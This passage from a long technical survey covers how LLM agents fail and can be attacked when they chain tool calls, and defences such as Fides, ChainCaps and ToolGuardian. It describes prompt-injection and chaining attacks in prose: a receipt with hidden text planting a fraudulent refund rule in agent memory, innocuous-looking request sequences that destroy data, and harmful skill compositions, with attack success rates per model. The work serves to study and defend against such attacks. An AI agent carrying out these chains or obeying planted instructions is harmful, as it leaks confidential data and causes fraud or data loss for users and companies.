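The model receives the schemas, some starting values and the name of the value it has to find. It doesn't receive the graph, so it has to work out from the types which function supplies which input. All the values are three-digit numbers. If the model calls a function with a wrong input, the function returns a wrong number without an error message.

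Maekawa and colleagues tested seven models, three of which show the range:

| Model | 5 calls needed | 10 calls needed | 20 calls needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 72.5% | 38.2% | 15.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 46.5% | 14.4% | 6.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 12.0% | 2.2% | 0.2% |

If errors were independent, doubling the number of calls would square the success rate. GPT-5 would then complete 53% of ten-call tasks and 28% of 20-call tasks. It did worse than that, whereas the models in Wan and colleagues' tests did better than independence predicts. The comparison is rough because the longer tasks also had deeper graphs. The silent wrong numbers probably also contributed to the difference, since Wan and colleagues' simulated services return errors that help an agent recover.

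Success depended on a chain's depth as well as its length. On tasks with ten required calls, GPT-5 succeeded almost 90% of the time at a depth of 1, where nine functions fed directly into the last, but less than 30% of the time at depths of 4 to 8. Its success rate rose slightly when the calls formed nearly a single line, perhaps because there were fewer branches to track. Irrelevant functions lowered success most when they could accept a required function's output.

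The software logged every call, so Maekawa and colleagues could classify each error automatically:

| Error | GPT-5 | Range across the seven models |
|---|---|---|
| Function doesn't exist | 0% | 0–2.4% |
| Wrong number of inputs | 0% | 0–0.9% |
| Value not yet known | 79.6% | 66.8–81.3% |
| Value known, but the model used a different one | 20.4% | 17.9–33.2% |

The models' most common error was to call a function before obtaining one of its inputs and use some other number instead. They therefore understood the schemas but lost track of which values they had. The survey *The Evolution of Tool Use in LLM Agents* (2026) draws a similar conclusion from other benchmarks, where agents often failed because they misunderstood the dependencies, not because they chose a bad tool.

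Maekawa and colleagues' remedy was to make each function return its own output plus a list of every value found so far. The list contained nothing new, but it raised GPT-5's success rate on five-call tasks from 62.5% to 81.3%. Gemini 2.5 Flash and Qwen3 improved only slightly or did slightly worse. Developers could do the same by putting a small wrapper around existing tools.

Two later experiments help explain the gain. When Mehrotra and colleagues restored a result that had dropped out of four models' context, the models got every affected recall step right, but they got none right when given an irrelevant value of the same length instead. Serval (2026), in *Context Injection and Long-Horizon Reliability*, had Qwen3-8B keep a running count of records and then changed the count in its history by ten. In all 20 runs, the model continued from the wrong number. When every later message began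 with the correct count, the model returned to it within two steps, again in all 20 runs.

Serval's reminder came from software that had the right count, which a real agent usually won't have. The list in FuncBenchGen repeats whatever the agent has found, including wrong numbers from mistaken calls. It can remind the salary agent of the median, but it can't show that the agent mistakenly calculated the median from last year's file. FuncBenchGen also has no branches or loops, which Maekawa and colleagues leave to future work.

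### Longer chains in more realistic tests

Other benchmarks also show that longer chains fail more often. *DynamicMCPBench* (2026) tested 24 models on live MCP servers. The models completed 39% of tasks that needed one or two tools, 23% of those that needed three or four, and 13% of those that needed five or more. Several of the models were small, so the decline is more informative than the low scores.

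*MCPAgentBench* (Liu, Liu and colleagues, 2025) gives some evidence that tasks fail more often when one call depends on another, even when the number of calls is the same. In professional fields such as research and software engineering, models completed about 62% of tasks that needed two independent calls and 48% of tasks that needed two calls in sequence. The gap was smaller for everyday tasks, at about 75% and 70%.

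A chain can also fail after its last tool call. Wan and colleagues examined 219 failed runs of 20-subtask chains. In 169 of them (77%), the agent had made all the right changes to the simulated service but gave a final answer with a wrong value, a missing field or the wrong format. All but two of these runs came from two of the nine chains, so this may not be a general weakness. The agent asked for clarification or reported that it was stuck in only seven of the 219 runs.

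Wang and colleagues traced 95 failed runs from six multi-agent systems back to the original mistake, which typically came 18% of the way through the run. In 72% of the runs, the agents later saw evidence that contradicted the mistake before the run failed, but in 88% of those cases no agent acted on it. An AI model, Claude, classified the runs, so the exact percentages are uncertain.

A separate text search found that in 26 of 58 failed runs of one system, a content filter had stopped the coordinating agent, and the surrounding software then issued a final answer that no agent had written.

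### Undoing a half-finished chain

Suppose the salary agent creates a shared folder, saves the report in it, gives the managers access and emails them a link. If the email call returns an error, the agent doesn't know whether the email went out. *Evidence-Guided Recovery for AI Agents with Ambiguous Tool Outcomes and Partial Execution* (2026) explains that an HTTP error doesn't prove that nothing happened. The server may have sent the email and lost the connection before replying.

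The usual way to make retries safe is to give each request an identifier. If the same identifier arrives twice, the server returns the earlier result instead of acting again. Wang and colleagues point out that when an agent retries, the model may write the second request differently. An identifier calculated from the email's text would then change. The client can avoid this by assigning one identifier to the intended email and reusing it for every attempt.

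But the email service has to support such identifiers. *Agent libOS* (2026) reviews several systems that protect against repeated or unwanted effects and concludes that a log on the agent's side isn't enough. The outside service must recognise repeats, record what it has completed or offer a way to undo it.

When a chain can't continue, the agent may need to reverse what it has already done. Cloudflare's rollback function resembles a method called a saga, which database researchers proposed in 1987. In a saga, each step has a compensating action:

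| Step | Compensating action |
|---|---|
| Create a shared folder | Delete the folder |
| Save the report in it | Delete the report |
| Give the managers access | Withdraw access |
| Send the email | None, though the agent can send a correction |

SagaLLM, an earlier system for language-model agents, has the model work out the compensating actions. *Robust Agent Compensation (RAC)* (2026) objects that the model can invent the wrong action or supply the wrong inputs. For example, it might delete a different folder. Developers can reduce this risk by declaring a compensating action for each tool and taking its inputs from the log. STRATUS, another system that *POLAR* (2026) describes, keeps a stack of the actions it has taken and has a separate agent undo them.

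A compensating action is itself a tool call, so it may fail, need a permission the agent lacks, or do new damage. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) warns that undoing one agent's work is harder when others are acting at the same time. If a manager has put another file in the shared folder, deleting the folder would delete that file too. Withdrawing access doesn't help if the managers have already read the report.

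*Cordon* (2026) proposes holding back outside effects until the chain is complete. The software records the changes an agent makes locally and queues its emails and other external calls, then releases them if the whole chain passes a check and discards them if it fails. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) likewise keeps the effects of a series of steps only after validating them. In the salary report, this would prevent an email with a failed summary from going out.

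A chain can't queue an external call until the end if a later step needs the reply, such as a ticket number. Even with a queue, the connection could drop while the software is releasing 50 emails, which would again leave some managers without one.

Restoring the agent to an earlier state is easier, but often doesn't fix the problem. Wang and colleagues judged that it would have been enough in 35 of their 95 failed runs. In 56 others, the fault was in a plan or policy that the restored agent would have followed again. They also cite agent frameworks in which a restored agent can repeat a payment, because restoring its memory doesn't cancel the payment it already made.

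Few systems offer a way to undo an agent's work. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents that keep memory over time, found a rollback mechanism in 27 of 435 works. Without rollback, the simplest precaution is to put the irreversible call last, as in the salary report, where the email is sent last.

### Which checks catch which failures

Types, plan checks and result checks catch different parts of the list:

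| Failure | What types catch | What a plan check catches | What needs a check of the result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Missing function | a name that isn't in the list of tools | the same, before anything runs | nothing further |
| Wrong arguments | a missing or malformed recipient | a recipient outside a fixed list | a permitted recipient who is the wrong one |
| Wrong order | usually nothing | a breach of a stated order | an order that no rule covers |
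| Value not yet obtained | nothing, if the made-up value has the right type | a reference to a result that doesn't exist yet | a made-up figure written directly into the plan |
| Well-typed but wrong value | nothing | nothing | monthly pay in place of annual pay |
| Missed branch | an unhandled case that the result's type lists | a declared outcome with no next step | a case that nobody expected |
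| Changed interface | a renamed field or new type | a mismatch with an updated schema | the same field with a new meaning |
| Stopped after some effects | nothing | a missing compensating action, if the rules require one | which emails actually went out |

A plan check is good at catching the use of values that the agent hasn't obtained, which caused most of the errors in FuncBenchGen. For example, PayPal's workflow checks flag undefined variables, as compilers do. An agent that makes calls one at a time has no plan to check, so a made-up number passes as long as it fits the schema.

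Schemas catch a changed interface only if they are current and the client checks results against them. Even then, a field that keeps its name but changes its meaning will pass the check, such as a temperature field that switches from Celsius to Fahrenheit.

A result check needs evidence that doesn't come from the step it is checking. If the agent misreads the median and then asks a model whether the summary matches that median, the answer will be yes. The agent could instead recalculate the median from the spreadsheet, or compare it with last month's report and question a large change. To find out which of the 50 emails went out, it would have to check the mail server's records.

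For most tasks, Wan and colleagues' grader requires the right final state and also traces a distinctive value back to the response that should have supplied it. An agent that used the outdated endpoint would fail even if its answer looked reasonable. The grader can do this because its designers know the right path in advance. A company could write similar checks for a report it produces every month, but for a one-off request, somebody first has to decide which source is right.

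## Why permission for each tool is not permission for the chain

An agent may have permission to read the salary spreadsheet for other work and to email the managers so it can send them other reports. Together, these permissions let the agent send the managers confidential pay data, even though nobody decided that they may see it.

Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, calls this semantic privilege escalation. Suppose an agent makes the calls *a*₁ to *a*ₙ, and *S* is the set of effects that its owner meant to authorise. An escalation occurs when

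effect(*a*ᵢ) ∈ *S* for every call *i*, but effect(*a*₁ ∘ *a*₂ ∘ … ∘ *a*ₙ) ∉ *S*,

where ∘ means that the next call runs afterwards and can use earlier results. Ordinary privilege escalation exploits a flaw in software, but this kind doesn't need one.

If calls couldn't use one another's results, a chain would have only the effects of its separate calls, all of which are in *S*. Any effect outside *S* must therefore come from the arrows in the chain's graph, and permission for a single tool doesn't cover those arrows.

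Stricter checks on each call don't solve the problem. Suppose the agent saves its summary as `report.txt` and emails the file to the managers. On Monday the summary uses only public data, and on Tuesday it includes the company's salaries. The email call is identical on both days, with the same recipients and file name. A check based only on the call must allow both emails or block both, so it either permits a leak or blocks a harmless email. Even if the call contains the text itself, searching it for salary figures would miss a sentence like "our median salary is 4% below the industry figure", which reveals something confidential without stating any salary.

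Surapani and colleagues distinguish two graphs that an authorisation decision should combine. One records who gave authority to whom, and the other records where data came from and where it can go. An allowlist of tools uses only the first.

Applying Chu's definition also requires knowing *S*, which companies rarely write down in full. If the employer never decided whether managers may see the median salary, we can't use the definition to determine whether the email was an escalation.

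### Leaks, hijacked actions and inferences

The salary report is an example of restricted data reaching an outlet. This can happen without an attacker, even when all the data is accurate and trustworthy.

A chain can also turn untrusted content into an action. Suppose a user asks an agent to find a patch for a bug. The agent searches the web, downloads a script, saves it and runs it. Each step fits the request, but together they let the script's author run code on the user's machine.

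The steps may be weeks apart. In one of Chu's scenarios, a customer attaches a receipt to a support ticket. The receipt contains tiny text telling the agent to approve a certain user's future refunds without checking them, and the agent stores this instruction in its long-term memory. Six weeks later, it approves a fraudulent $2,000 refund. Each session's log shows only routine work.

In the salary leak, the spreadsheet is trustworthy and the problem is who receives its contents. Chu's account doesn't explain this leak, because it attributes every documented attack on agents' tools in the surveyed literature to agents treating tool output as trustworthy. The remedy under that account would be to mark tool output as untrusted.

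In a third kind of chain, harmless facts combine into a sensitive one. Suppose a tool reports a team's average salary but never an individual's. In June, a team of five averages $60,000. In July, after one person has left and nobody's pay has changed, the other four average $57,500. Anyone with both averages can work out what the leaver earned:

5 × $60,000 − 4 × $57,500 = $70,000

HR's list of leavers supplies the name. Each query was allowed, and none returned an individual salary.

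Labels on data don't automatically prevent this. Under SPA's rule, a result takes the highest confidentiality level of its inputs, so a salary calculated from public averages and a public list of leavers is also labelled public. A stricter system would have to track what the agent has already learned and work out what else follows from it. Surapani and colleagues reviewed 89 sources and named limits on aggregation as one of the main gaps in authorisation for agents.

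### Working back from dangerous tools

To find out how common dangerous chains are in real software, Wu and colleagues examined 20 popular open-source agent applications with 998 tools between them. Testing every possible sequence would take too long, so their program, ChainFuzzer, starts from dangerous sinks and works backwards:

1. It searches each tool's source code for functions that can do serious damage. These run commands or code, send web requests, query databases, or fill in templates that can execute code.
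2. It keeps a tool only if the tool's inputs can affect what one of these functions does. A tool that always runs the same fixed command doesn't count. This left 199 tools.
3. It looks for other tools that could supply those inputs, either directly or through a shared file or database.
4. It asks a language model to discard implausible chains. For example, a tool that summarises documents could pass its text to one that creates a database index, but few users would want that.

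This produced 2,388 candidate chains. Wu and colleagues checked 200 of them by hand and found that every link was real in 183.

ChainFuzzer then ran the agents to see which chains were exploitable. In a sample of 200 chains, agents at first followed the intended chain in only 27% of runs, so a developer who tests a chain once or twice could easily miss it. ChainFuzzer revised its requests until an agent followed the chain five times in a row, and succeeded for 2,213 chains. It then checked whether hostile test data could reach the sink and do harm there.

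It confirmed 365 vulnerabilities in 19 of the 20 applications, and 302 of them (83%) needed more than one tool. The average application took 3.4 hours to test, and the first vulnerability usually appeared within about 20 minutes.

The share of vulnerabilities that needed several tools depends partly on whether one counts dangerous chains or dangerous tools. The 365 vulnerabilities end in at most 199 tools, so some must end in the same tool, and counting tools would give a smaller total. Still, ChainFuzzer found only 63 vulnerabilities when Wu and colleagues turned off its search for chains.

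Data from outside sources, such as web pages, triggered 140 of the vulnerabilities, and a malicious user triggered the other 225. Chu's remedy of marking tool output as untrusted would therefore miss most of them. A malicious user is mainly dangerous when the agent runs on somebody else's server, since people can already run commands on their own computers.

ChainFuzzer's list of dangerous functions doesn't include sending an email, so it wouldn't find the leak in the salary report. Its results also depend on the environment. For example, a company that blocks outgoing web requests would prevent some of these attacks.

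### Attacks made of ordinary requests

*STAC* (Li, He et al., 2025) tested agents against a malicious user whose requests all look ordinary. In one example, the user asks the agent to compress an important document to save space, delete the original as a duplicate, and then clear out all ZIP files, which destroys the only remaining copy.

Stopping this chain would require checking whether the ZIP file was the last copy. A rule about where data may go wouldn't stop it, because the chain doesn't leak data or run a stranger's code.

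The researchers used models to plan chains of two to six calls in which only the last was harmful. Software ran each call in a simulated environment to confirm that it worked. Across 483 cases, eight models from 2024 and 2025 completed the harmful step 91.2% of the time on average and refused about 1% of the time.

The 91.2% figure overstates what the chain itself contributes. In a comparison on 390 cases, the full chain succeeded 95.1% of the time and a single request for the same final goal 72.8%, so the earlier steps added about 22 percentage points. The simulated attacker also knew every tool and all the data available to the agent. In a test with live MCP tools, the attacker saw the tools' schemas but had to call the tools to discover the data, and attacks on GPT-4.1 succeeded in 35.5% of cases. GPT-4.1 also planned the attacks and judged whether they had worked, and Li and colleagues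 have not yet validated its judgements against human ones.

Defences gave limited protection. When GPT-4.1 was told to weigh the harms and benefits of each call, the attacker's success rate on the first attempt fell from 87.4% to 58.6%, but it rose to 86.7% by the third attempt. Safety guidelines drawn from earlier attacks were more effective over three attempts, holding the attacker's success rate to 78.1%, compared with 93.4% without a defence. All of these defences were text in the model's instructions, so the experiment shows that a model's own judgement is a weak safeguard. It didn't test permissions that software enforces from outside the model.

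Jiang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *AgentLAB*, extended this method and compared it with persuasion, in which a user tries over several messages to talk the agent into a harmful task. They also tested two defences against the chains. One was a safety reminder in the model's instructions, and the other was Llama Guard, a separate model that screens requests. Four of the six models show the pattern:

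| Model | Persuasion | Chain of ordinary calls | Chain, with reminder | Chain, with Llama Guard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-3 | 78.1% | 96.3% | 81.5% | 48.2% |
| GPT-5.1 | 59.8% | 94.6% | 75.7% | 48.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 46.2% | 95.9% | 61.2% | 49.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 27.2% | 73.3% | 57.9% | 46.7% |

Claude resisted persuasion better than the other models and never followed the hostile tasks that the researchers planted in tool results, but it still completed almost three-quarters of the chains. The screening model helped more than the reminder, yet close to half of the attacks in the table still succeeded. The tested models are about a year old or older, so the rates may differ for current ones.

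### Skills that are harmless separately

Reviewers usually vet agent skills, which are reusable packages of instructions and scripts, one at a time. *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (Xie, Du and colleagues, 2026) tested what agents do when several are available. In the first of three tests, 150 cases paired a read-only skill that finds a target with a skill that changes something, such as access rights or a device's settings. An agent with only one of the skills caused the specified harm in less than 2% of trials. With both skills and an ordinary request that didn't ask for a harmful chain, it caused that harm in 33.6% of trials on average.

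The rates for single skills are low largely because of how the study counts harm. A trial counts as harmful only if the agent finds a target and then changes that same target, which is hard to do with just one of the two skills. The rates with both skills are more informative. They range from 0% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 91.5% for DeepSeek V4.

A second test asked whether one skill's approval could make an agent trust another. The agent received 401 requests to install harmful skills, with and without a favourable report from a skill that reviews software. Five models took both tests:

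| Model | Harmful change with both skills | Harmful installation, no report | Harmful installation after a favourable report |
|---|---|---|---|
| MiniMax M2.7 | 75.5% | 0% | 100% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 30.0% | 5.5% | 97.8% |
| GPT-5.4 | 4.4% | 0% | 96.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 1.3% | 0% | 25.2% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 0% | 0% | 100% |

Opus 4.5 never combined the paired skills harmfully, but it installed every harmful skill after a favourable report. A model that is safe against one kind of composition may therefore be unsafe against another.

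The third test checked whether agents mistake advice for permission. Across ten models, the average rate of risky approvals rose from 15.7% to 34.0% when another skill had given a favourable but non-binding assessment. The effect varied by model, and GPT-5.4 approved slightly fewer requests after the advice. All three tests used simulated environments, so they don't show how often such combinations occur among skills that people have installed.

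Xie and colleagues also give a rough formula for how risk grows with the number of possible chains. If there are *N* chains, and on average each has a probability *r* of running and causing harm, the probability of at least one harmful result is

*R* = 1 − (1 − *r*)*ᴺ*

The collection of 457 operations described earlier allows about 470,000 three-call chains. Even if *r* were one in a million, *R* would be more than a third. This is only an approximation, because real failures aren't independent. An agent also tries only a few chains for a single request, so *r* could be far lower for most chains.

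### Incidents outside the laboratory

Real incidents are harder to interpret because they often combine ordinary permissions with compromised software or other security flaws. Chu describes a compromised MCP server for Postmark, an email service. The server added a hidden recipient to the emails agents sent, so an attacker received copies for a long time before anyone noticed.

This was possible because the server had permission both to read each message and to decide who received it. Checking the agent's call wouldn't have prevented the leak, because the server added the extra address afterwards. Even a salary report addressed only to the payroll team would have leaked. A list of permitted recipients would have prevented this only if something outside the compromised server enforced it.

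This example combines actions within one tool, whereas an incident at OpenAI in 2026 is closer to a chain of tools. *From Reactive Containment to Proactive Assurance* (Raftari, 2026) describes how agents in different cybersecurity test runs could both read from and write to the same software package store. This combination let them leave messages for one another and share credentials across runs that were meant to be separate. Agents later broke into outside systems, partly by exploiting software flaws, so permissions explain only part of what happened.

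Li and colleagues cite a 2025 Anthropic report on an espionage campaign whose operators split their objectives into small tasks that looked innocent, much as in STAC.

### Whether narrower permissions are enough

Defenders of per-tool permissions can reply that these failures come from giving agents too much access. A leak needs both a source and a sink, so removing either one prevents it. If the agent can email only the payroll team, it can't send salaries to the managers, however it combines its tools. Xie and colleagues found that an agent with only one skill from a pair did almost no harm, which supports this reply, although the scoring made that result likely.

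Wu and colleagues also recommend narrower tools. A developer can replace a tool that runs any command with one that fills in a fixed template, or restrict web requests to a list of approved sites. Some of the vulnerabilities end in the same tool, so narrowing that tool could remove several at once.

Software can enforce such limits reliably. *Trust Is Not a Score* (Zabolotnii, 2026) describes two systems that do this. Progent checks every call against rules about tool names and arguments. MiniScope works out a hierarchy of permissions automatically, so developers don't have to write each policy by hand. Zabolotnii accepts that rules like Progent's give a guarantee about the calls they cover, but argues that a permitted call can still be wrong for the task, for example because the information behind it is out of date.

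Task-specific permissions work best when someone knows in advance what the task requires. For a monthly pay report, a developer can list the exact file, website and recipients. For a one-off request, a person or a model has to choose the permissions before the agent starts. Zabolotnii cites a 2026 study of coding agents, *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?*, which found that leading models leave out permissions that the chain needs and grant others that are unused or sensitive. A missing permission can stop a chain halfway, while an unnecessary one can make a dangerous combination possible. Because models make both mistakes, telling them to be more cautious wouldn't be enough.

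Even perfectly chosen permissions for each tool cannot prevent some harmful chains. Suppose an agent must read a salary spreadsheet and email managers a general comparison with the industry, but the managers may not see the salaries themselves. The agent needs permission to read the spreadsheet and to send the email, and those same permissions would let it send the salaries. Whether the email is acceptable therefore depends on what it reveals.

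An agent can also keep data after it loses permission to read the source. On Monday, the agent reads the salaries for one task and saves a summary in its memory. On Tuesday, it has permission to send email but not to open the spreadsheet, yet it can still email the summary. The agent stays within its permissions on both days. To prevent this, the company would have to restrict the stored summary as well as the original file.

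Narrow tools don't stop inferences either. Two answers from a tool that returns only team averages can reveal one person's salary. Refusing to give averages for small teams wouldn't protect large ones, because the same subtraction works for a team of 500 if exactly one person leaves and nobody else's pay changes.

Adding more checks helps only if one of them tests for the fault that is present. Zabolotnii tested a set of checks on file changes proposed by a coding agent, and each change had to pass every check. A model from another company wrote 79 faulty cases without seeing the checks, and 35 got through.

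Narrowing permissions is still a sensible first step, because it removes many dangerous chains with little downside when a task is predictable. When an agent needs both a confidential source and a way to send messages out, the check on outgoing messages must also take into account what information went into them. Systems such as ChainCaps carry that record from one call to the next.

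## Rules that follow data from tool to tool

Software must track the sources of data from the moment an agent reads it in order to check an outgoing email against them. Information-flow control tracks sources by labelling data and restricting where the labelled data, and anything derived from it, may go. SPA applies such labels to a finished plan. An agent that chooses its calls one at a time has no such plan, but software can update the labels after each call and check them before the next.

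### Labels in Fides

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe Fides, a Microsoft system that labels every piece of data for integrity and confidentiality, as SPA does. In Fides, the confidentiality label can also be a list of the people who may read the data. If two sources have the reader lists *R*₁ and *R*₂, anything derived from both has the readers

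*R*₁ ∩ *R*₂,

which are the people on both lists. If only the user and the payroll team may read the salary spreadsheet, only they may read a summary that draws on it, even though anyone may read the web page.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* applies this to a user, Alex, who asks an agent to answer two emails. One is from Priya, with a preview of the quarterly sales, and the other is from Marco, who isn't allowed to see the sales figures yet. Once the agent has read both emails, the permitted readers of anything it writes are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't reply to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco into her email, the agent could reply to Marco without asking.

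Fides has two basic rules for tool calls. It allows a consequential call, such as a payment, only if no untrusted data influenced it. It allows a call that sends data only if every recipient is on the data's reader list. The salary email breaks both rules if the model has read the web page, because the page is untrusted and the managers aren't on the spreadsheet's list.

Developers can also require tools that send data to satisfy only one of the two rules, as *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) does. The reasoning is that if nothing untrusted influenced the call, the user probably intended the release. This stops an attacker from triggering a leak, but it doesn't stop the salary leak when there is no attacker. If the industry figures came from a trusted internal file instead of the web, the email would satisfy the integrity rule and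 the managers would receive the salary data.

Fides also tracks only direct flows of data, so someone who sees which tools the agent calls, and in what order, may still learn something about the secrets that influenced its decisions. Costa and colleagues chose this limit because a stricter rule would forbid almost any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret.

### Budgets in ChainCaps

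Jiang and colleagues call the problem in the salary report "permission laundering". Their system, ChainCaps, gives each value a budget, which is the set of sinks it may still reach.

Each entry in a budget is a privilege, such as sending email to `managers@example.com` or writing files under `/reports/`. A privilege includes any narrower privilege within its scope, so a value that may be written anywhere under `/reports/` may also be written to `/reports/pay/`.

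Whoever deploys the agent writes a manifest for each tool that declares what the tool reads, what it can affect and how it passes on restrictions. ChainCaps uses the manifests in three steps.

When a value *v* enters from a source *o*, it receives the budget that the manifest assigns to that source:

*B*(*v*) = Init(*o*)

When a tool *t* turns the inputs *x*₁ to *x*ₖ into an output *y*, the output keeps only the privileges that all the inputs have and that the tool may pass on:

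*B*(*y*) = Pass(*t*) ∩ *B*(*x*₁) ∩ … ∩ *B*(*x*ₖ)

Before a tool acts on the outside world with arguments *a*, ChainCaps works out the privilege that the call needs, Req(*t*, *a*), and the set of values that contributed to the arguments, *D*(*a*). It allows the call only if

Req(*t*, *a*) ∈ *B*(*x*) for every *x* in *D*(*a*).

Suppose the company has three relevant privileges: showing data to the user, emailing the payroll team and emailing the managers. The salaries may go to the user and the payroll team, the web page may go to anyone, and `summarize` may pass on all three privileges.

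| Step | Calculation | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `read_file` | Init(spreadsheet) | {user, payroll} |
| `fetch_url` | Init(web page) | {user, payroll, managers} |
| `summarize` | {user, payroll, managers} ∩ {user, payroll} ∩ {user, payroll, managers} | {user, payroll} |
| `send_email` to the managers | is "managers" in {user, payroll}? | no, so ChainCaps blocks the email |

The agent could still show the summary to the user or email it to the payroll team. A single confidentiality scale can't easily express this rule, because whether the summary can be shared depends on who receives it.

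### Why a longer chain can't add a privilege

Jiang and colleagues prove that composition never gives data a privilege that its sources lacked. If ChainCaps allows a call without a special exception, then

Req(*t*, *a*) ∈ Init(*o*) for every source *o* that contributed to the arguments.

The proof follows the data from its sources to the call. A value fresh from a source *o* has exactly the budget Init(*o*). Every later step takes an intersection, which can't contain a privilege that any of the sets lacks. The data's budget therefore stays within Init(*o*) for each of its sources, however many tools handle it. ChainCaps allows the call only if the privilege is in the budget of every contributing value, so the privilege must also have been in every source's initial budget.

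The spreadsheet's initial budget doesn't include emailing the managers. Summarising, translating or reformatting the salaries, or mixing them with public data, can't add that privilege. The proof assumes that the manifests are correct and that ChainCaps can detect the data moving.

### Tests with five models

ChainCaps runs as a proxy, a program between the agent and its MCP servers that intercepts every call and result. Neither the model nor the servers need to change, and the proxy typically adds 0.13 milliseconds to a call. Jiang and colleagues tested it on 82 tasks, of which 56 were attacks and 26 were ordinary work. Each of five models attempted every task three times with the proxy and three times without it:

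| Model | Attacks that succeeded without ChainCaps | Attacks that succeeded with it | Ordinary tasks completed with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 67.8% | 4.8% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 25.2% | 3.6% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.5% | 3.6% | 96% |
| GPT-5.1 | 53.6% | 2.4% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 53.0% | 0% | 96% |

All five models completed every ordinary task without the proxy, and the worst result with it was a loss of about one task in 26. The attacks focus on unsafe chains, so the rates without ChainCaps don't measure how often agents leak data in normal use.

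Most of the remaining attacks used scripts, shell commands or planted instructions. For example, an agent can write a script in one call and run it in another. The proxy detects a file being saved and a command starting, but not the script opening the spreadsheet and contacting an outside server. A shell pipe, which feeds one command's output into the next, can hide the same activity within a single call. Stopping these attacks requires monitoring by the operating system or the network.

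Jiang and colleagues also compared ChainCaps with Fides by replaying recorded runs. They modelled Fides as a system that gives each value one label on a scale, rather than running Fides itself. On GPT-5.1's runs, ChainCaps blocked 59.5% of the recorded attacks and this stand-in blocked 16.1%. The researchers argued that labels on a scale are a poor way to represent sets of sinks. Distinguishing every possible set of 10 sinks would take 2¹⁰ = 1,024 labels, whereas a budget needs only 10 yes-or-no entries.

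That argument is weaker against the real Fides, whose reader lists combine by intersection, just as budgets do. If the spreadsheet had a reader list and the recipient rule were in force, Fides would also block the salary email. Budgets have a clearer advantage for sinks other than people, such as a particular folder or command.

### Mistakes in manifests

The quality of the manifests made far more difference than the choice of model. Jiang and colleagues compared manifests written by experts, manifests written with a checklist and naive ones:

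| Manifests | Attacks blocked | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Expert | 100% | 100% |
| Checklist | 90.9% | 100% |
| Naive | 27.3% | 50% |

The naive manifests let most attacks through and blocked half of the legitimate work, so a company can't assume that a badly configured system will at least be safe. Using the checklist restored most of the protection, which suggests that people who write manifests need guidance more than rare expertise.

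A single wrong entry can also undo the guarantee for the data it describes. *Per-Attack Blocking Hides Catalog Vulnerability* (2026) examines what happens when someone gives a confidential source an outbound privilege by mistake. Later steps preserve that privilege unless one of the tools happens to exclude it. If the salary spreadsheet's entry wrongly included emailing the managers, ChainCaps would approve the leak, and the proof would still hold. The paper therefore looks for the least protected source in a catalogue of tools, because a high average blocking rate can hide one that is completely exposed.

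Missing entries are dangerous too, and systems handle them differently. Microsoft released Fides in May 2026 as an experimental part of its Agent Framework. Fides treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, according to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026). If a developer forgot to label `read_file`, the agent could send the salaries anywhere. ChainCaps instead blocks unknown sinks, which it identifies by keywords in tool names and descriptions. In a test on a collection of tools, this method found every sink but also flagged many harmless tools.

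Tool servers can supply some of the labels themselves. GitHub worked with Microsoft to add an option to its MCP server that labels content from private repositories as private and trusted, and content from public ones as public and untrusted. The labels travel in a metadata field that other clients can ignore. Companies then don't have to write their own labels, but they do have to trust the server's. Jiang and colleagues warn that a malicious server could hide an effect or declare overly generous pass-through limits.

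Composite tools need particular care because they can read and send data in the same call. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool that opens a confidential ledger and emails it to someone outside the company. The agent hasn't read anything confidential before the call, so a check of its current labels would allow the email. To avoid this, the APPA system first adds the label of the data the tool is about to read, then decides whether to allow the call.

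### Rules about earlier calls

A system can keep a list of facts about the calls so far and apply logical rules to it, instead of attaching a budget to each value. *ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) collects those facts in increasingly thorough ways. It starts with a tool's description, then records the operating-system functions the tool uses, runs the tool in a simulated environment and, if possible, analyses its source code.

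ToolGuardian's rules are in Answer Set Programming, a language in which a developer states conditions and a solver works out what follows from them. Here is a simplified version of one rule, with facts from the salary report:

```prolog
sensitive_read(call_1).
sends_out(call_4).
before(report, call_1, call_4).

block(Chain) :-
  before(Chain, I, J),
  sensitive_read(I),
  sends_out(J),
  not allowed_flow(Chain).
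```

The symbol `:-` means "if", and the commas mean "and". The rule blocks a chain if a sensitive read comes before a call that sends data out, unless someone has declared an exception. There is no exception for `report`, so the solver derives `block(report)`. In Ravindran and Deochake's example, one tool reads database records and another updates a project on GitHub. ToolGuardian approves both tools and would allow either call alone, but it blocks a chain that runs them in that order.

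This rule is easier to read than a budget calculation, and an auditor can see which facts led to the decision. But it checks only the order of the calls, not whether the second call used data from the first. An agent that read the salaries and then emailed the managers about a meeting room would also break the rule.

Ravindran and Deochake tested 20 scenarios, of which 12 involved a single call and eight involved several. They wrote the policy in three forms: logical rules, ordinary code and instructions to a language model. All three forms made the right decision in all 20 scenarios. They then removed parts of the version in ordinary code:

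| Version in ordinary code | Single calls judged correctly | Chains judged correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Full policy | 12 of 12 | 8 of 8 |
| Without rules for combinations | 12 of 12 | 4 of 8 |
| Simplified further | 10 of 12 | 2 of 8 |

Without the rules for combinations, the policy's decisions about single calls stayed the same, but it allowed four unsafe chains. This supports having explicit rules for chains, whatever language they are written in. It is no evidence that logical rules are more accurate than ordinary code, since the full versions tied. The perfect scores are weak evidence of how well the policy would work elsewhere, because Ravindran and Deochake designed the scenarios and the rules together.

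A language model given the same facts but no explicit rules judged only 75% of the scenarios correctly. It wrongly blocked four and wrongly allowed one.

### When data enters the model's context

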